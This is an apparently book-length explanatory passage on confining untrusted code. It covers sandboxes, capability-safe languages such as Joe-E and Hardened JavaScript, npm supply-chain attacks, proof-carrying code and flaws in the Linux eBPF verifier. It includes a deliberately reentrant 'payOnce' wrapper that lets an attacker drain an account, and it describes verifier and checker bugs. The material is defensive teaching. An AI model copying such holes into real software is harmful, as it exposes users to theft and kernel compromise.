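Designers can make a sandbox harder to escape by reducing what its boundary depends on. Linux has a strict mode in which a process can make only four system calls: read from an open channel, write to one, exit, and resume after an interruption. A thumbnail decoder could work under these rules if the service gave it all the memory it needs in advance. The reviewer would then have to check four system calls instead of several hundred.

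## Capability-safe languages: code that can use only what it is handed

A sandbox puts one boundary around a whole process or library, and all the code inside usually has the same rights. The thumbnail service's web server has to read uploads, save thumbnails and use the network. Every library in the same process can do those things too, even one that only sorts lists. An attacker who adds a few lines to the sorting library can delete every stored video. Porting the library to Rust wouldn't help, because safe Rust lets any code delete a file by name.

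*Ambient authority* is access that code has because of where or for whom it runs, without anyone handing it over. *Paradigm Regained* (Miller and Shapiro, 2003) gives the example of Solitaire. The game needs to draw in its window, receive clicks and perhaps save a file. On an ordinary computer, it can also search the player's email for interesting items and sell them to the highest bidder. Doing so would break no rule of the operating system, so there is no bug to fix.

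A capability-safe language removes ambient authority, so each part of a program can use only what another part has given it. Habitat Chronicles (2017) traces the idea to a 1966 paper by Jack Dennis and Earl Van Horn on how an operating system could share a machine between programs.

### File names and open files

Miller and Shapiro explain the difference with two Unix commands that both copy a file:

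```
cp foo.txt bar.txt
cat < foo.txt > bar.txt
```

In the first, the shell (the program that reads the user's commands) gives `cp` two pieces of text, and `cp` has to find and open the files itself. The user might have typed any name, so `cp` needs the right to open every file the user can open.

In the second, the shell opens both files and gives `cat` two open channels, without the file names. On an ordinary Unix machine `cat` still has all the user's rights, but it needs only the two channels for this job. If the system took those rights away, `cat` would still work but `cp` would fail.

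A file name is text, so whoever receives it needs separate permission to use the file. An open channel to the file both identifies it and grants the right to use it, which makes the channel a capability. OpenSSH's monitor hands over terminals in the same way.

Users needn't notice these restrictions. *Robust Composition* (Miller, 2006) describes CapDesk, an experimental desktop on which programs start with almost no access. Double-clicking a spreadsheet or picking it in the "open file" window gives the program access to that one spreadsheet. The user has to choose the file anyway, so there is no extra permission prompt to answer.

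### Four ways to get a reference

Object-capability languages apply this to the objects inside a program. An object is a bundle of data with functions that act on it, and other code can use the object only if it has a reference to it. The language must be memory-safe, or an attacker could forge a reference by writing an address into memory. Miller lists the only ways in which an object called Bob can come to hold a reference to another called Carol:

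- *Initial conditions:* Bob has the reference when the program starts.
- *Parenthood:* Bob creates Carol.
- *Endowment:* Alice, who already has a reference to Carol, creates Bob and builds the reference into him.
- *Introduction:* Alice has references to both, and passes Carol to Bob in a message.

Two groups of objects with no references between them can therefore never become connected, because no object can pass a reference from one group to the other. These rules don't cover plain data. Code that can work out a number or a password can use it, even if no other code passed it along.

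Most popular languages break the rules of capability safety in some way. C++ lets a program turn an ordinary number into a pointer. Java has global variables that any code can read and change, so two objects can communicate or swap references even if neither was given a reference to the other.

### Judging code without reading it

Here is a version of the thumbnail service's main loop in JavaScript. We assume for now that the language enforces the rules and that the sorting and decoding libraries start with no references to anything outside themselves.

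```js
function makeThumbnails(videos, thumbnails, addToLog) {
  const order = sort(videos.sizes());               // line 1
  const decoder = makeDecoder(addToLog);            // line 2
  for (const i of order) {                          // line 3
    const picture = decoder.decode(videos.read(i)); // line 4
    thumbnails.save(i, picture);                    // line 5
  }
}
```

A reviewer can find the limits of each library's power by noting what the program hands to it:

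| Library | What it receives | The worst it can do |
|---|---|---|
| `sort` | A list of video sizes | Return a wrong order, leave videos out, or never finish |
| `decoder` | The contents of each video, and `addToLog` | Return wrong pictures, show one customer's frames in another's thumbnail, write anything in the log, or never finish |

Neither library can delete a video or contact the internet. The reviewer knows this from reading five lines, without opening the decoder, which may have hundreds of thousands. The conclusion would hold even if an attacker had rewritten both libraries from scratch.

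The reviewer does have to read `addToLog`. The decoder holds a reference to that function, which holds a reference to the log file, so tracing references alone can't rule out that the decoder will erase the log. Reading the function might show that it only adds a line at the end. Miller and Shapiro distinguish *permission*, which is direct access, from *authority*, which is everything a piece of code can bring about, directly or through others. The decoder has the authority to make the log file longer without having permission to use the file.

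Values that a library returns also need attention, as with RLBox. If `picture` is a plain grid of pixels, saving it is safe. But if it is an object with its own functions, `thumbnails.save` might call one and pass it a reference that the decoder was never meant to have.

### Joe-E: taking things out of Java

*Joe-E* (Mettler, Wagner and Close, 2010) made Java capability-safe by removing features. Every Joe-E program is also a normal Java program, so it runs with the usual tools. A verifier checks the source one file at a time and rejects any file that uses something forbidden.

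| Forbidden in Joe-E | Reason |
|---|---|
| Native methods, which run code from outside Java | They can do anything, including forging references |
| Global variables that can change | Any code could communicate or pick up references through them |
| Library functions that reach files or the network without a capability | They are ambient authority |
| The feature that lets code ignore the label `private` | It exposes what another object has hidden |
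| Exceptions that contain changeable objects | They can carry a reference to code that shouldn't have it |
| Custom `finalize` methods, `finally` blocks, and catching serious errors | They let an attacker's code use an object that an error has left half-finished |

The rule about exceptions shows how easily a reference can leak. Suppose Bob keeps a capability private but lends it to Chuck. Chuck throws an exception, an error report that passes up through the callers until one of them handles it. If the exception contains the capability and Bob doesn't catch the exception, it reaches Alice, who called Bob. She can take the capability out and use it. Someone reviewing Bob's code would see nothing wrong, because the leak depends on what Chuck puts in the exception.

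Java's standard library took more work to make safe than the language did. A file object should give access to only one file, but Java's has a method, `getParentFile`, that returns the folder above. Code given one file could call it repeatedly until it reached the top of the disk, and from there open every other file. Another function is useful to capability programmers because it opens a named file within a given folder, but if the folder is missing (`null`), Java treats the name as a path from the top of the disk. Mettler and colleagues blocked both and wrote a replacement for the second that checks for a missing folder. They call selecting the safe library functions *taming*.

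For a reviewer, the benefit is that a private field really is private. This class keeps a log that other code can add to but not alter:

```java
public final class Log {
    private final StringBuilder content = new StringBuilder();
    public void write(String s) { content.append(s); }
}
```

In ordinary Java, a reviewer can't tell from the class alone that old entries are safe, because code anywhere in the program could use the feature that ignores `private`. The reviewer would have to read the entire program to rule this out, but in Joe-E, these few lines are enough.

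Mettler and colleagues do the same for money in an online game. A purse object can take money from another purse of the same currency, after checking that the amount isn't negative and that the other purse holds enough. Only code with a reference to the currency itself can create new money. To confirm that players can't create any, a reviewer only has to read two short classes, however many players and add-ons use them.

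### Decoders without a memory

Joe-E can also verify that an object is *immutable*, meaning that neither it nor anything it refers to can ever change. Mettler and colleagues use this to limit a picture decoder that comes from an untrusted source:

```java
public interface Decoder extends Immutable {
    byte[][][] decode(byte[] imagedata);
}
```

The interface accepts and returns only bytes, so nobody can pass the decoder a capability through it. The decoder's state can't change, so it can't store part of one picture and reveal it while decoding the next. The worst a malicious decoder can do to a picture is decode it wrongly, and a reviewer can confirm this from the interface alone. The service therefore doesn't need to start a new process for every video to stop the decoder from mixing up customers' frames.

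A related property is *purity*. A function is pure if its result depends only on what it receives and it changes nothing else. In an earlier project, Mettler, Wagner and two colleagues worked out how to verify purity in Joe-E and adapted an existing library of more than 10,000 lines that reads HTML. Once the verifier confirms that such a library is pure, reviewers no longer need to consider when or how often other code calls it, or what ran before. They still have to check that it reads HTML correctly.

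The larger case study was Waterken, a server that runs web applications for developers who don't trust one another, all inside one Java process. It has about 13,000 lines of Joe-E and 4,000 of ordinary Java. After each request, Waterken must save either all of an application's changes or none of them. If it saved a deposit into one purse but not the matching withdrawal from another, a customer could gain money by repeating the transfer. In ordinary Java, an application could keep data in a global variable or a file that the server wouldn't check. Joe-E forbids both, so the server can find every change by following references from the objects that the application used.

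An application could also keep a reference to a saved object and alter it later, when the server was no longer monitoring it. The designers prevented this by requiring each request and whatever it returns to be immutable. The verifier enforces this rule on all applications, so reviewers of the saving code don't have to read any application's code.

The language's own designers reported these results. They describe what a reviewer no longer has to read, but they did not measure how much time that saves or how many flaws reviewers then miss. The verifier does not help with the 4,000 lines of Java, which need as much care as any other Java. Joe-E also does not limit processor time or memory, so a malicious decoder can still stop the service by running forever.

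### The DarpaBrowser review

Capability design had faced a harder test in 2002, when DARPA paid for a security review of an experimental web browser called the DarpaBrowser. The browser was based on Miller's language E, which Joe-E drew on heavily. Its renderer was a plug-in that might be malicious, and the rest of the browser was supposed to confine it. The reviewers were David Wagner, later one of Joe-E's designers, and E. Dean Tribble, who had written papers with Miller.

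Miller reports that the reviewers found many vulnerabilities. According to Mettler and colleagues, one group came from the taming of Java's libraries, which limited E programmers to library functions on an approved list. The list included several functions that broke the capability rules. One such function can be enough to defeat the whole design. A renderer that calls it gets access that nobody handed it, and a reviewer who traced references through the browser's own code would not see where the access came from.

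The reviewers were close to the project, which might be a reason to discount their praise but not the flaws they found. The review shows that the part everybody must trust can be large even when each rule is simple. Java's libraries have thousands of functions, and someone has to know how each behaves in odd cases like the missing folder. This work is closer to ordinary security review than to a mechanical check, but a team has to do it only once for each library, and every program in the language can then rely on the result.

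Joe-E's designers approved a library function only after checking it, and left it out if they were unsure. They still describe taming as a substantial weakness of their approach and say they may have approved something they shouldn't have. Their caution also kept the approved part of the library small.

### Malicious packages

Modern programs contain far more code from strangers than Java programs did in 2002. JavaScript developers get most of this code from npm, a public registry of free packages, and a package usually brings in others that the developer didn't choose. An ordinary application can easily depend on hundreds of packages, and each runs with all of the program's rights.

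In September 2025, attackers tricked one maintainer into giving up his login and published malicious versions of 18 packages, including `chalk`, which colours text in a terminal. The packages had a combined total of more than two billion downloads a week. The malicious code ran in web browsers and redirected cryptocurrency payments to the attackers. A worm called Shai-Hulud appeared the same month, and a second version followed in November. The worm stole developers' passwords and access keys and used them to infect other packages those developers maintained. The US cybersecurity agency CISA said the September version compromised more than 500 packages.

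Code that colours text doesn't need access to the network or to anybody's payments. Hardened JavaScript, a capability-safe form of JavaScript, can withhold that access. It descends from the language E through Caja, a Google project for putting untrusted content in web pages, as Miller describes in *From E to EcmaScript and back again*. Hardened JavaScript makes two main changes to ordinary JavaScript.

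One safeguard in Hardened JavaScript is to freeze the objects that all JavaScript code shares. Normally, any package can replace the built-in function that goes through a list item by item, and the replacement then receives every list that other packages process with that function. After a program calls `lockdown()`, no code can alter the built-in functions.

The other change is the *compartment*, which runs a piece of code with its own set of global names. Any code in a normal web page can call `fetch` to contact a server, but code in a compartment can do so only if the program that created the compartment has provided `fetch`.

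Rewriting hundreds of packages to receive their capabilities as arguments would be hopeless, so a tool called LavaMoat does something cruder. It puts each package in a separate compartment and reads a policy file that lists what the package may use. An entry for an invented package might look like this:

```json
"photo-resizer": {
  "globals":  { "console.log": true },
  "builtin":  { "fs.readFile": true },
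  "packages": { "sort-list": true }
}
```

This package can print messages, read files and use the package `sort-list`, but it can't write files or contact the internet. LavaMoat scans each package's code and drafts the policy from what the code appears to use, so nobody has to write hundreds of entries by hand.

With such a policy in force, the malicious version of `chalk` would have had no `fetch` to intercept, and any `fetch` it defined would have been visible only inside its own compartment. But if a developer had used LavaMoat to generate a new policy after the update, that policy would have granted the malicious code all the access it needed. The protection therefore depends on someone reading the changes to the policy. This is easy for a package like `chalk`, because the new policy would contain a line giving network access to a library that colours text. A program can detect that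 the policy has grown, and a person can tell that something is wrong without knowing anything about the attack.

The compartments would not have stopped Shai-Hulud, because it ran when a developer installed the package, before the application started. npm lets packages run scripts during installation. LavaMoat includes a separate tool that blocks these scripts unless the package is on the developer's list.

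MetaMask, a cryptocurrency wallet that runs as a browser extension, is the best-known program that ships with LavaMoat. Wallets have good reason to be early adopters, since in 2018 an attacker took over the popular npm package `event-stream` and used it to steal from users of another wallet, Copay. MetaMask shows that a large commercial program with many ordinary npm packages can run under LavaMoat, but one wallet isn't much evidence of how well LavaMoat stops attacks.

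### What it costs to freeze JavaScript

Some harmless packages stop working under Hardened JavaScript. The most obvious are those that add features to the built-in objects, as older browsers often required. They have to make their changes before Hardened JavaScript freezes those objects, and the developer has to trust them more than other packages.

A less obvious problem comes from an old quirk of JavaScript. This code looks as if it affects only one object:

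```js
const point = {};
point.toString = () => "(0, 0)";
```

JavaScript objects normally inherit a `toString` function from a shared built-in object. If that shared object is frozen, assigning a new `toString` to an object such as `point` fails. In strict mode the program stops with an error; otherwise it carries on with the inherited function. Hardened JavaScript works around this for the properties that packages most often override, but packages occasionally override others.

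Hardened JavaScript also rejects source code that contains the text `import(`, which could load new code from outside the compartment. It searches the text without fully parsing the program, so it also rejects packages that only mention `import(` in a comment. LavaMoat avoids some of these rejections by rewriting such comments before it runs the code. The toy rule about the word "delete" makes the same tradeoff.

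### Packages that need dangerous rights

Miller pictures a program's exposure as a grid. Each row is a component, and its height is the chance that an attacker corrupts it. Each column is an asset, and its width is the damage an attacker could do with it. A cell is filled if its component can reach its asset, and the total area of the filled cells is the expected damage.

A hypothetical wallet has 500 packages, each with a 1 in 10,000 chance per month of turning malicious, and stolen keys would cost its users $1 million. If every package can reach the keys, the expected loss is 500 × 0.0001 × $1 million, or $50,000 a month. If only ten can, it is $1,000 a month. There is still about a 5 percent chance each month that at least one package turns malicious, but it usually won't be able to reach the keys.

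The calculation assumes that attackers choose packages at random. If they know about the restrictions, they will concentrate on the ten packages, so the real improvement would be less than fiftyfold. It could still be large, since reviewers can concentrate on the same ten.

Those packages may be hard to restrict further. In December 2024, attackers published versions of `@solana/web3.js`, a library for the Solana blockchain, that sent them users' private keys. The library has to handle private keys and contact servers, so a policy that listed its rights by name would have allowed both. A stricter design would have given it a function that could contact only the user's chosen Solana server. Even then, malicious code could have hidden the keys in a transaction on a public blockchain, where the attackers could read them. Bernstein's complaint about sandboxes also applies to libraries like this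 one.

### Wrappers that leak

Capability programmers often hand over a wrapper instead of a powerful object. A wrapper is a small object that passes on only some requests to the object behind it. The `addToLog` function is a wrapper around a file. David Redell described another wrapper, the *caretaker*, in 1974. It passes on every request until its owner switches it off, so Alice can give Bob access to a folder today and withdraw that access tomorrow.

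Miller and Shapiro argue that capability systems can support this kind of withdrawal, which other researchers had said was impossible because Bob keeps any reference he receives. They say Bob does keep his reference, but it leads to a caretaker that no longer does anything.

However, the simple caretaker doesn't cover objects that the folder returns. If Bob asks the folder to open a file, he gets a direct reference to a file object, which keeps working after Alice has withdrawn the folder. Miller says the simple version is safe only if Alice can rely on the wrapped object not to give out direct access to itself. Where she can't, he recommends a *membrane*, which puts a new caretaker around every reference that passes through in either direction and switches them all off together.

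Other mistakes depend on the order of events. This wrapper is supposed to allow one payment:

```js
function payOnce(pay) {
  let used = false;
  return recipient => {
    if (used) throw Error("already used");
    pay(recipient);
    used = true;
  };
}
```

If `pay` notifies the recipient before it returns, and the recipient is working with the attacker, the notification can trigger a second call while `used` is still false. The attacker can repeat this until the account is empty. Moving `used = true` above the payment fixes it. Every reference here goes where the programmer intended, so tracing references wouldn't reveal the fault.

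A *model checker* tries every possible sequence of messages in a small model of the program. *Object-Capability as a Means of Permission and Authority in Software Systems* (2019), a survey of the formal research, covers Toby Murray's 2010 thesis, which analysed capability patterns this way, and OCPL, a logic for proving that a pattern holds whatever the untrusted code around it does. Wrappers are good candidates for such methods because they are short and many programs reuse them. But a result for one setting may not apply in another. For example, a wrapper that is safe when messages arrive one at a time may fail when two arrive together.

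Platforms can leak references too. Researchers who traced the links between JavaScript objects found flaws in a major browser that let a script from one website access another site's objects. They also defeated the protections of a library meant to combine code from different sites safely.

### Channels that aren't references

Two components that hold no references to each other may still communicate. One can keep the processor busy to signal a 1 and stay idle to signal a 0, while the other reads the bits by timing its own work. Miller and Shapiro exclude such channels because their model describes only what programs can do by sending messages.

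Receiving a signal like this requires some way to measure time, which a capability-safe language can withhold. New compartments in Hardened JavaScript have no access to the current time or to random numbers unless the program supplies them. Joe-E code has no direct access to a clock either. Withholding the clock works for a decoder, which doesn't need to know the time, but a package that handles network connections usually needs one to decide when to stop waiting. Even without a clock, a component that can exchange messages with an outside server could use the server's replies to measure time.

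### Why most languages haven't adopted the model

The main obstacle is existing code. Java and Python programs open files by name in many places, and a language that forbade this would break most of those programs. Mettler and colleagues say that Joe-E is for new programs and that making old Java code conform was never a goal.

If one component of a Joe-E program is still in ordinary Java, it can ignore `private` and interfere with all the others, so reviewers must read it as carefully as before. A team that converts nine components out of ten has only a tenth of the code left to review in full, but converting that much takes a long time.

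Programmers also have to design differently. If a function deep inside a program needs a file, it can't open one itself. Each caller has to pass the file down, starting from the part of the program that has it. Many programmers already do this to make testing easier, and call it dependency injection. Miller says that people who learn the capability style tend to keep it even when security doesn't matter. But Mettler and colleagues expect most programmers to need training. They suggest that an expert could design the interfaces between components while others write the code inside them.

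Java's designers tried another approach, the Security Manager, which checked each sensitive operation against a central policy. Few applications used it, and Java 24 permanently disabled it in 2025.

Capabilities have done better between programs than inside them, because there is less old code to break. A WebAssembly module can call only the functions that its host gives it. The seL4 kernel uses capabilities to control what each process can reach, and CHERI builds them into the processor. AI models may now make it practical to convert the old code inside programs. A model that can port Bun to Rust can presumably also rewrite functions so that they receive files instead of opening them, and a verifier like Joe-E's could check every line of the result. People would still have to decide which old library functions are safe to allow.

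## Proof-carrying code: making the supplier show that code is safe

Joe-E's verifier needs a program's source code and accepts only one language, but a receiver often gets machine code from a stranger. *Safe Kernel Extensions Without Run-Time Checking* (Necula and Lee, 1996) proposed a method for this case. The supplier produces a formal proof that the program obeys the receiver's rules and sends it with the program. The receiver only has to run a short program that checks the proof. Necula and Lee called the combination of program and proof *proof-carrying code*.

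### From program to formula

The method has four steps:

1. The receiver publishes a *safety policy*. It defines which actions are safe, what the receiver promises about the data it will hand over, and which logical rules a proof may use.
2. A *condition generator*, which is part of the policy, turns the program into a logical formula. If the formula is true, the program can't break the policy.
3. The supplier finds a proof of the formula and attaches it to the program.
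4. The receiver runs the generator on the program it has received. A proof checker then confirms that every step of the proof follows the rules and that the last step is this formula.

If the check succeeds, the receiver can run the program as often as it likes without checking anything again.

Suppose the thumbnail service lets camera makers supply small routines that set the brightness of thumbnails. The service gives each routine a list of n brightness readings and promises that n is at least 1. Its policy allows a routine to read item i only if 0 ≤ i < n. One maker's routine takes the reading in the middle of the list:

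```
i = n / 2             // line 1, rounding down
x = brightness[i]     // line 2
return x              // line 3
```

The generator works backwards from the end. Line 3 reads nothing from the list, so it adds no condition. Line 2 reads item i, so 0 ≤ i < n has to be true just before it. Line 1 sets i to n/2, so the generator puts n/2 in place of i. With the service's promise added, the formula is:

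for every n, if n ≥ 1 then 0 ≤ ⌊n/2⌋ and ⌊n/2⌋ < n

(The brackets mean rounding down.) Suppose the policy's rules include two facts about halving: half of a positive number, rounded down, is never negative, and it is always smaller than the number itself. The proof is then short:

1. n ≥ 1, by the service's promise.
2. 0 ≤ ⌊n/2⌋, from step 1 and the fact that the half is never negative.
3. ⌊n/2⌋ < n, from step 1 and the fact that the half is smaller.
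4. 0 ≤ ⌊n/2⌋ and ⌊n/2⌋ < n, from steps 2 and 3.

Without the promise there would be no proof, because an empty list would require 0 < 0.

The rules must describe processor arithmetic, in which large results wrap around. In ordinary arithmetic, adding a number and then subtracting it gives back the original value. Necula and Lee's rules allow this simplification only if the proof has shown that the original value fits in 64 bits.

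A policy can also do more than keep a program within the bounds of a list. In one of Necula and Lee's examples, the kernel keeps a table in which each user has a tag and a data word. A user's program may always read both, but may change the data only if the tag isn't zero. Their example program uses seven instructions to add 1 to the data when the change is allowed. The receiver took 1.4 milliseconds to check the proof.

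### Why the supplier need not be honest

Imagine that an attacker intercepts the brightness routine and changes it before it reaches the service.

- If line 1 becomes `i = n`, the routine reads past the end of the list. The new formula requires n < n, which is false, so no valid proof exists.
- If line 1 becomes `i = n / 3`, the routine is still safe, but the old proof is about n/2. The service rejects the routine until somebody supplies a proof that matches.
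- If line 3 becomes `return 0`, the formula stays the same and the old proof passes. The routine is now useless, but it still obeys the policy.

Changing the proof doesn't help the attacker either. The result is an invalid proof, which the checker rejects, or another valid proof of the same formula.

The service therefore doesn't need to check who wrote the routine or who has handled it since. A digital signature, by contrast, shows only where a program came from, and Necula and Lee point out that people can sign an unsafe program as easily as a safe one. Confirming the origin wouldn't have stopped the malicious version of `chalk`, which came from its real maintainer's account.

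### Finding a proof and checking one

Finding two whole numbers above 1 that multiply to 8,051 takes some searching. If someone suggests 83 and 97, a single multiplication confirms the answer. Proofs are similar. Finding one can require a long search or a clever idea, but the checker only has to compare each step with a short list of rules.

Rice's theorem is no obstacle here, because a proof checker only has to decide whether a given text is a valid proof of a given formula. It rejects a safe program if nobody has found a proof, so it is conservative, like the Rust compiler.

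Loops are the main difficulty in finding proofs. Suppose another routine adds up all the readings, with i starting at 0 and rising by 1 until it reaches n. A proof can't go through every pass separately, because n could be any size. The supplier has to provide a *loop invariant*, a statement that is true at the start of every pass, such as 0 ≤ i ≤ n. The checker needs a proof of three things: the invariant is true when the loop begins, each pass keeps it true, and together with the loop's test (i < n) it shows that the read is safe. These proofs are routine once someone has thought of the invariant, but no general method always finds one, and Necula and Lee wrote theirs by hand.

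A supplier who can't find a proof can add a run-time check. If the routine tests whether i is less than n just before reading item i, that part of the formula becomes easy to prove, but the program runs slightly slower.

The receiver only has to check the proof. An attacker can put any amount of effort into searching for one, but the result must pass the same check. The supplier can also search with tools that nobody has reason to trust, including AI models, because a mistake in the search produces a proof that fails the check.

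### Packet filters in 1996

Necula and Lee tried the method on *packet filters*, small programs that inspect each packet arriving from a network and decide whether to pass it to an application. A filter runs inside the kernel for speed, so a faulty one could crash the machine or expose its memory. The policy let filters read only the packet and a 16-byte scratch area, write only to the scratch area, and jump only forwards, which rules out loops.

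They wrote four filters by hand in assembly language for the DEC Alpha, a fast processor of the time:

| Packets the filter accepts | Instructions | Size with proof | Time to check |
|---|---|---|---|
| All internet (IP) packets | 8 | 385 bytes | 0.8 ms |
| IP packets from one network | 15 | 516 bytes | 1.1 ms |
| IP or address-lookup packets between two networks | 47 | 1,024 bytes | 2.4 ms |
| TCP packets for one port | 28 | 814 bytes | 1.7 ms |

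The proofs were about three times the size of the code. After the researchers added some facts about arithmetic to an automatic prover, it found each proof in 5 to 10 seconds.

They then ran the filters on 200,000 packets recorded from a busy university network. The BSD Packet Filter (BPF), the usual method at the time, interprets each filter one instruction at a time and checks every memory access. The proof-carrying filters were about ten times faster than BPF and about 25 percent faster than the same filters with software fault isolation.

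Checking the proof takes longer than starting a filter by the other methods, so proof-carrying code is worthwhile only for a program that runs often enough. For the TCP filter, the time saved exceeded the checking time after 1,200 packets compared with BPF and after 28,000 compared with software fault isolation. At the network's rate of about 1,000 packets a second, that was roughly one second for BPF and half a minute for software fault isolation.

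The filters were also faster than versions in Modula-3, a memory-safe language, but that comparison is less fair because the filters were hand-tuned assembly and the Modula-3 versions were compiled. The larger doubt is whether the approach scales, since the longest filter had only 47 instructions and no loops, and Necula and Lee warn that proofs could in principle grow exponentially with program length.

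### Compilers that write the proofs

Few programmers want to write proofs about machine code, but a compiler can often do it for them. Necula explains in *Proof-Carrying Code* that if a policy covers only type safety, a loop invariant is generally just a list of the types of the values in use, such as "register 0 holds a list and register 1 holds a whole number". A compiler for a type-safe language already has this information.

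Ordinary compilers check the types in the source code and then discard them. A *certifying compiler* keeps them through every stage of translation and uses them to produce a proof about the finished machine code. *Foundational Proof-Carrying Code* (Appel, 2001) notes that a low-level program that passes its type check is safe even if earlier compiler stages have bugs.

Proof-carrying code addresses a weakness of Rust, whose guarantees depend on a very large compiler being correct. If a bug in a certifying compiler produces a program that could corrupt memory, the receiver's check fails and the program doesn't run.

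### Shrinking what the receiver must trust

The receiver still has to trust the condition generator, the logical rules and the checker. Necula and Lee's checker was about five pages of C, but a generator for a full system is much larger, and Appel cites one with 23,000 lines of C. A bug in the generator may produce the wrong formula, and a valid proof of the wrong formula doesn't show that the code is safe. The rules about types are another risk, because researchers had proved them sound only on paper, and often in simplified form.

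Appel's *foundational* version removes both the generator and the built-in typing rules. The receiver instead supplies a general mathematical logic and a model of how each processor instruction changes the registers and memory. In this model, an instruction that would break the policy has no next state. A program is safe if, wherever it starts in memory, it never reaches a state from which it can't continue. The supplier has to prove this directly, including any facts about types that the proof uses.

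Appel, Michael and colleagues (2003), in *A Trustworthy Proof Checker*, built such a system for Sun's Sparc processors with fewer than 2,700 trusted lines. The definitions account for 1,865 of them:

| Definitions the receiver must trust | Lines |
|---|---|
| Logic | 135 |
| Arithmetic | 160 |
| How numbers encode instructions | 460 |
| What each instruction does | 1,005 |
| What counts as safe | 105 |

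The rest is mostly a checker in C, short enough that a person could examine it even in machine language. Java virtual machines of the time had 50,000 to 200,000 lines of trusted code, and SpecialJ, a proof-carrying system for Java, had 36,000. Appel and colleagues mention that early Java browsers averaged one security bug per 3,000 lines. As a rough guide, that rate would give SpecialJ about 12 security bugs and the foundational system about one.

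Most of the trusted lines describe the processor, so a reviewer can check them against the manufacturer's manual. The reviewer must be careful, but doesn't have to guess what an attacker will try.

This approach means more work for whoever writes the proofs. By 2001 Appel's team had about 30,000 lines of proofs, and the system still covered only part of the Sparc's instruction set. Wu, Appel and Stump explain in *Foundational Proof Checkers with Small Witnesses* that built-in rules keep proofs short but may be wrong, while proofs that start from first principles can become huge. Their solution is to let the supplier add rules, along with a machine-checkable proof that the rules are sound.

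### Types as small proofs

Java is one of two widely used systems that apply a modest form of the idea. Its compilers produce *bytecode*, instructions for an imaginary processor, and a verifier checks the types before the code runs, for example to make sure that no instruction treats a number as a reference to an object. Modern compilers attach a table of the types that variables have at points where paths through the program meet. The verifier only has to confirm the table, which is quicker and simpler than working out the types itself.

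WebAssembly, which Firefox uses to confine its libraries, works similarly. Each block of code declares the types of the values it takes and produces, so a validator can check a program in a single pass. For instance, when the validator reaches an instruction that adds two 32-bit integers, it confirms that two such integers will be on the stack.

These types are much weaker than Necula and Lee's proofs. They can't express that an index is smaller than the length of a list, so Java checks each index at run time, and WebAssembly enforces its memory limits the same way. The guarantee also depends on the software that runs the code after the check. For example, a fault in Java's garbage collector can corrupt memory even if the bytecode is correct.

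### The verifier inside Linux

eBPF, a descendant of the BPF interpreter, lets Linux administrators load small programs into the kernel to direct network traffic, monitor performance or enforce security rules. Before a program runs, the kernel's eBPF verifier checks that it stays within its permitted memory, calls only approved kernel functions with suitable arguments, and finishes. In a talk listing these checks, Sisto (2025) notes that nobody has formally proved the whole verifier sound.

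The supplier of an eBPF program normally attaches no proof, so the verifier has to construct its own argument for safety by following the paths through the program and tracking which values each register could hold. This difficult analysis runs inside the kernel, where mistakes do the most harm. *The eBPF Runtime in the Linux Kernel* (2024) reports that developers change the verifier in every release to support new uses, which makes it hard to keep correct.

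Attackers can exploit these mistakes. A 2021 flaw made the verifier miscalculate the range of a 32-bit value, so it could accept a program that read or wrote outside its permitted memory. *SafeBPF* (2024) explains that an accepted program runs in the same memory as the kernel with no further checks, so such a flaw can give an attacker access to everything. Of the 41 vulnerabilities the paper counted, 28 concerned memory safety.

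Sources disagree about how many of eBPF's problems come from the verifier. Dasu, Santra and colleagues (2026), in *HEIMDALL*, say the verifier has more publicly catalogued vulnerabilities than any other part of eBPF. Chen, Ming and colleagues (2026), in *eBPF Security in the Wild*, find that most faults arise after verification, while programs run and interact with the rest of the kernel. The findings may differ because Chen and colleagues also count kernel fixes and automatic crash reports that never received a catalogue number. If they are right, even a perfect verifier would leave most of the faults.

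Researchers have started to check the verifier itself. The tool Agni translates the verifier's C code for jumps and arithmetic into logical formulas, and a solver then checks that the ranges the verifier predicts always include the real values. Agni has confirmed this for versions up to Linux 7.1-rc1, and kernel developers now run it routinely on new changes.

*Detecting Empty Abstractions and Pruning Dead Paths in the Linux eBPF Verifier* (Vishwanathan, Narayana and Nagarakatte, 2026) describes a class of faults that these proofs missed. The verifier keeps several records about each register. One might show that the value is exactly 15, and another only that it is between 0 and 15. If the program then tests whether the value is at most 10, the answer is always no. A version of the verifier that used only the looser record would explore the "yes" branch and get a range running from 15 down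 to 10. It then reset the range to "any value" and could reject a safe program because of code that never runs.

Agni's proofs cover only cases where at least one value fits all the records, and on such a branch none does. The faults didn't make accepted programs dangerous, but one wrongful rejection cut off the network for a whole cluster of servers after a restart. Vishwanathan and colleagues added a test that detects impossible branches and slows verification by about 1.5 percent on average. Linux has adopted the test's central function.

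### When the checker is the target

The verifier also rejects some safe programs because it doesn't track how values relate to one another. Suppose a program stores two records in an 800-byte buffer. The first takes u bytes, and the second starts at byte u and may use up to 800 − u bytes. The second record can't run past byte 800, because u + (800 − u) = 800. But the verifier tracks only that the second record's starting point and length are each between 0 and 800, so it calculates that the record might reach byte 1,600 and rejects the program.

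*bpf* (Sun, 2025), a set of proposed changes to Linux, revives proof-carrying code for such cases. When the verifier can't establish a condition, it sends that condition to a solver outside the kernel. The kernel doesn't need to trust the solver's more than 500,000 lines of code, because it accepts an answer only if a checker of about 5,000 lines approves the proof. For the buffer, the proof has 33 steps and takes up 852 bytes. With this help, the verifier accepted 403 of 512 programs it had previously rejected, and checking even an 8-megabyte proof took less than about three seconds.

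In *Keel*, Cai, Chang and Nagarakatte (2026) tried to prove this checker correct and found 13 bugs. For some kinds of proof step, the checker accepted any equation without checking it. These kinds made up about 7 percent of the steps in a set of real proofs.

Another bug involved a rule for comparing products. In ordinary arithmetic, if a is positive, then y × a is less than x × a exactly when y is less than x. The checker applied a version of this rule without ensuring that the products would fit. In 8-bit arithmetic, where numbers run from −128 to 127, the rule fails when y = 64, x = 0 and a = 2, because 64 × 2 wraps around to −128, which is less than 0 even though 64 is not.

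One false statement is enough to prove anything. Cai and colleagues used this rule to build a 13-step proof that the checker accepted for any condition. An attacker could have used that proof to get an unsafe program past a safety check.

Sun had tested the checker on a large collection of proofs and found no memory errors. But those proofs came from a solver designed to produce correct proofs, and an attacker can write any proof they like. Testing the thumbnail service on ten million real videos has the same problem.

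Cai and colleagues wrote a replacement checker, Keel, and proved that it accepts a proof only if the condition holds. They also proved that it never misuses memory and that its running time grows only in proportion to the size of its input, so a small malicious proof can't tie up the kernel. Keel is about 6,600 lines of C, and the proof that this code matches its specification is more than 52,000 lines long. The proof assistant Lean checks that proof, so nobody has to read it. Keel is also 1.3 times as fast as the checker it replaces.

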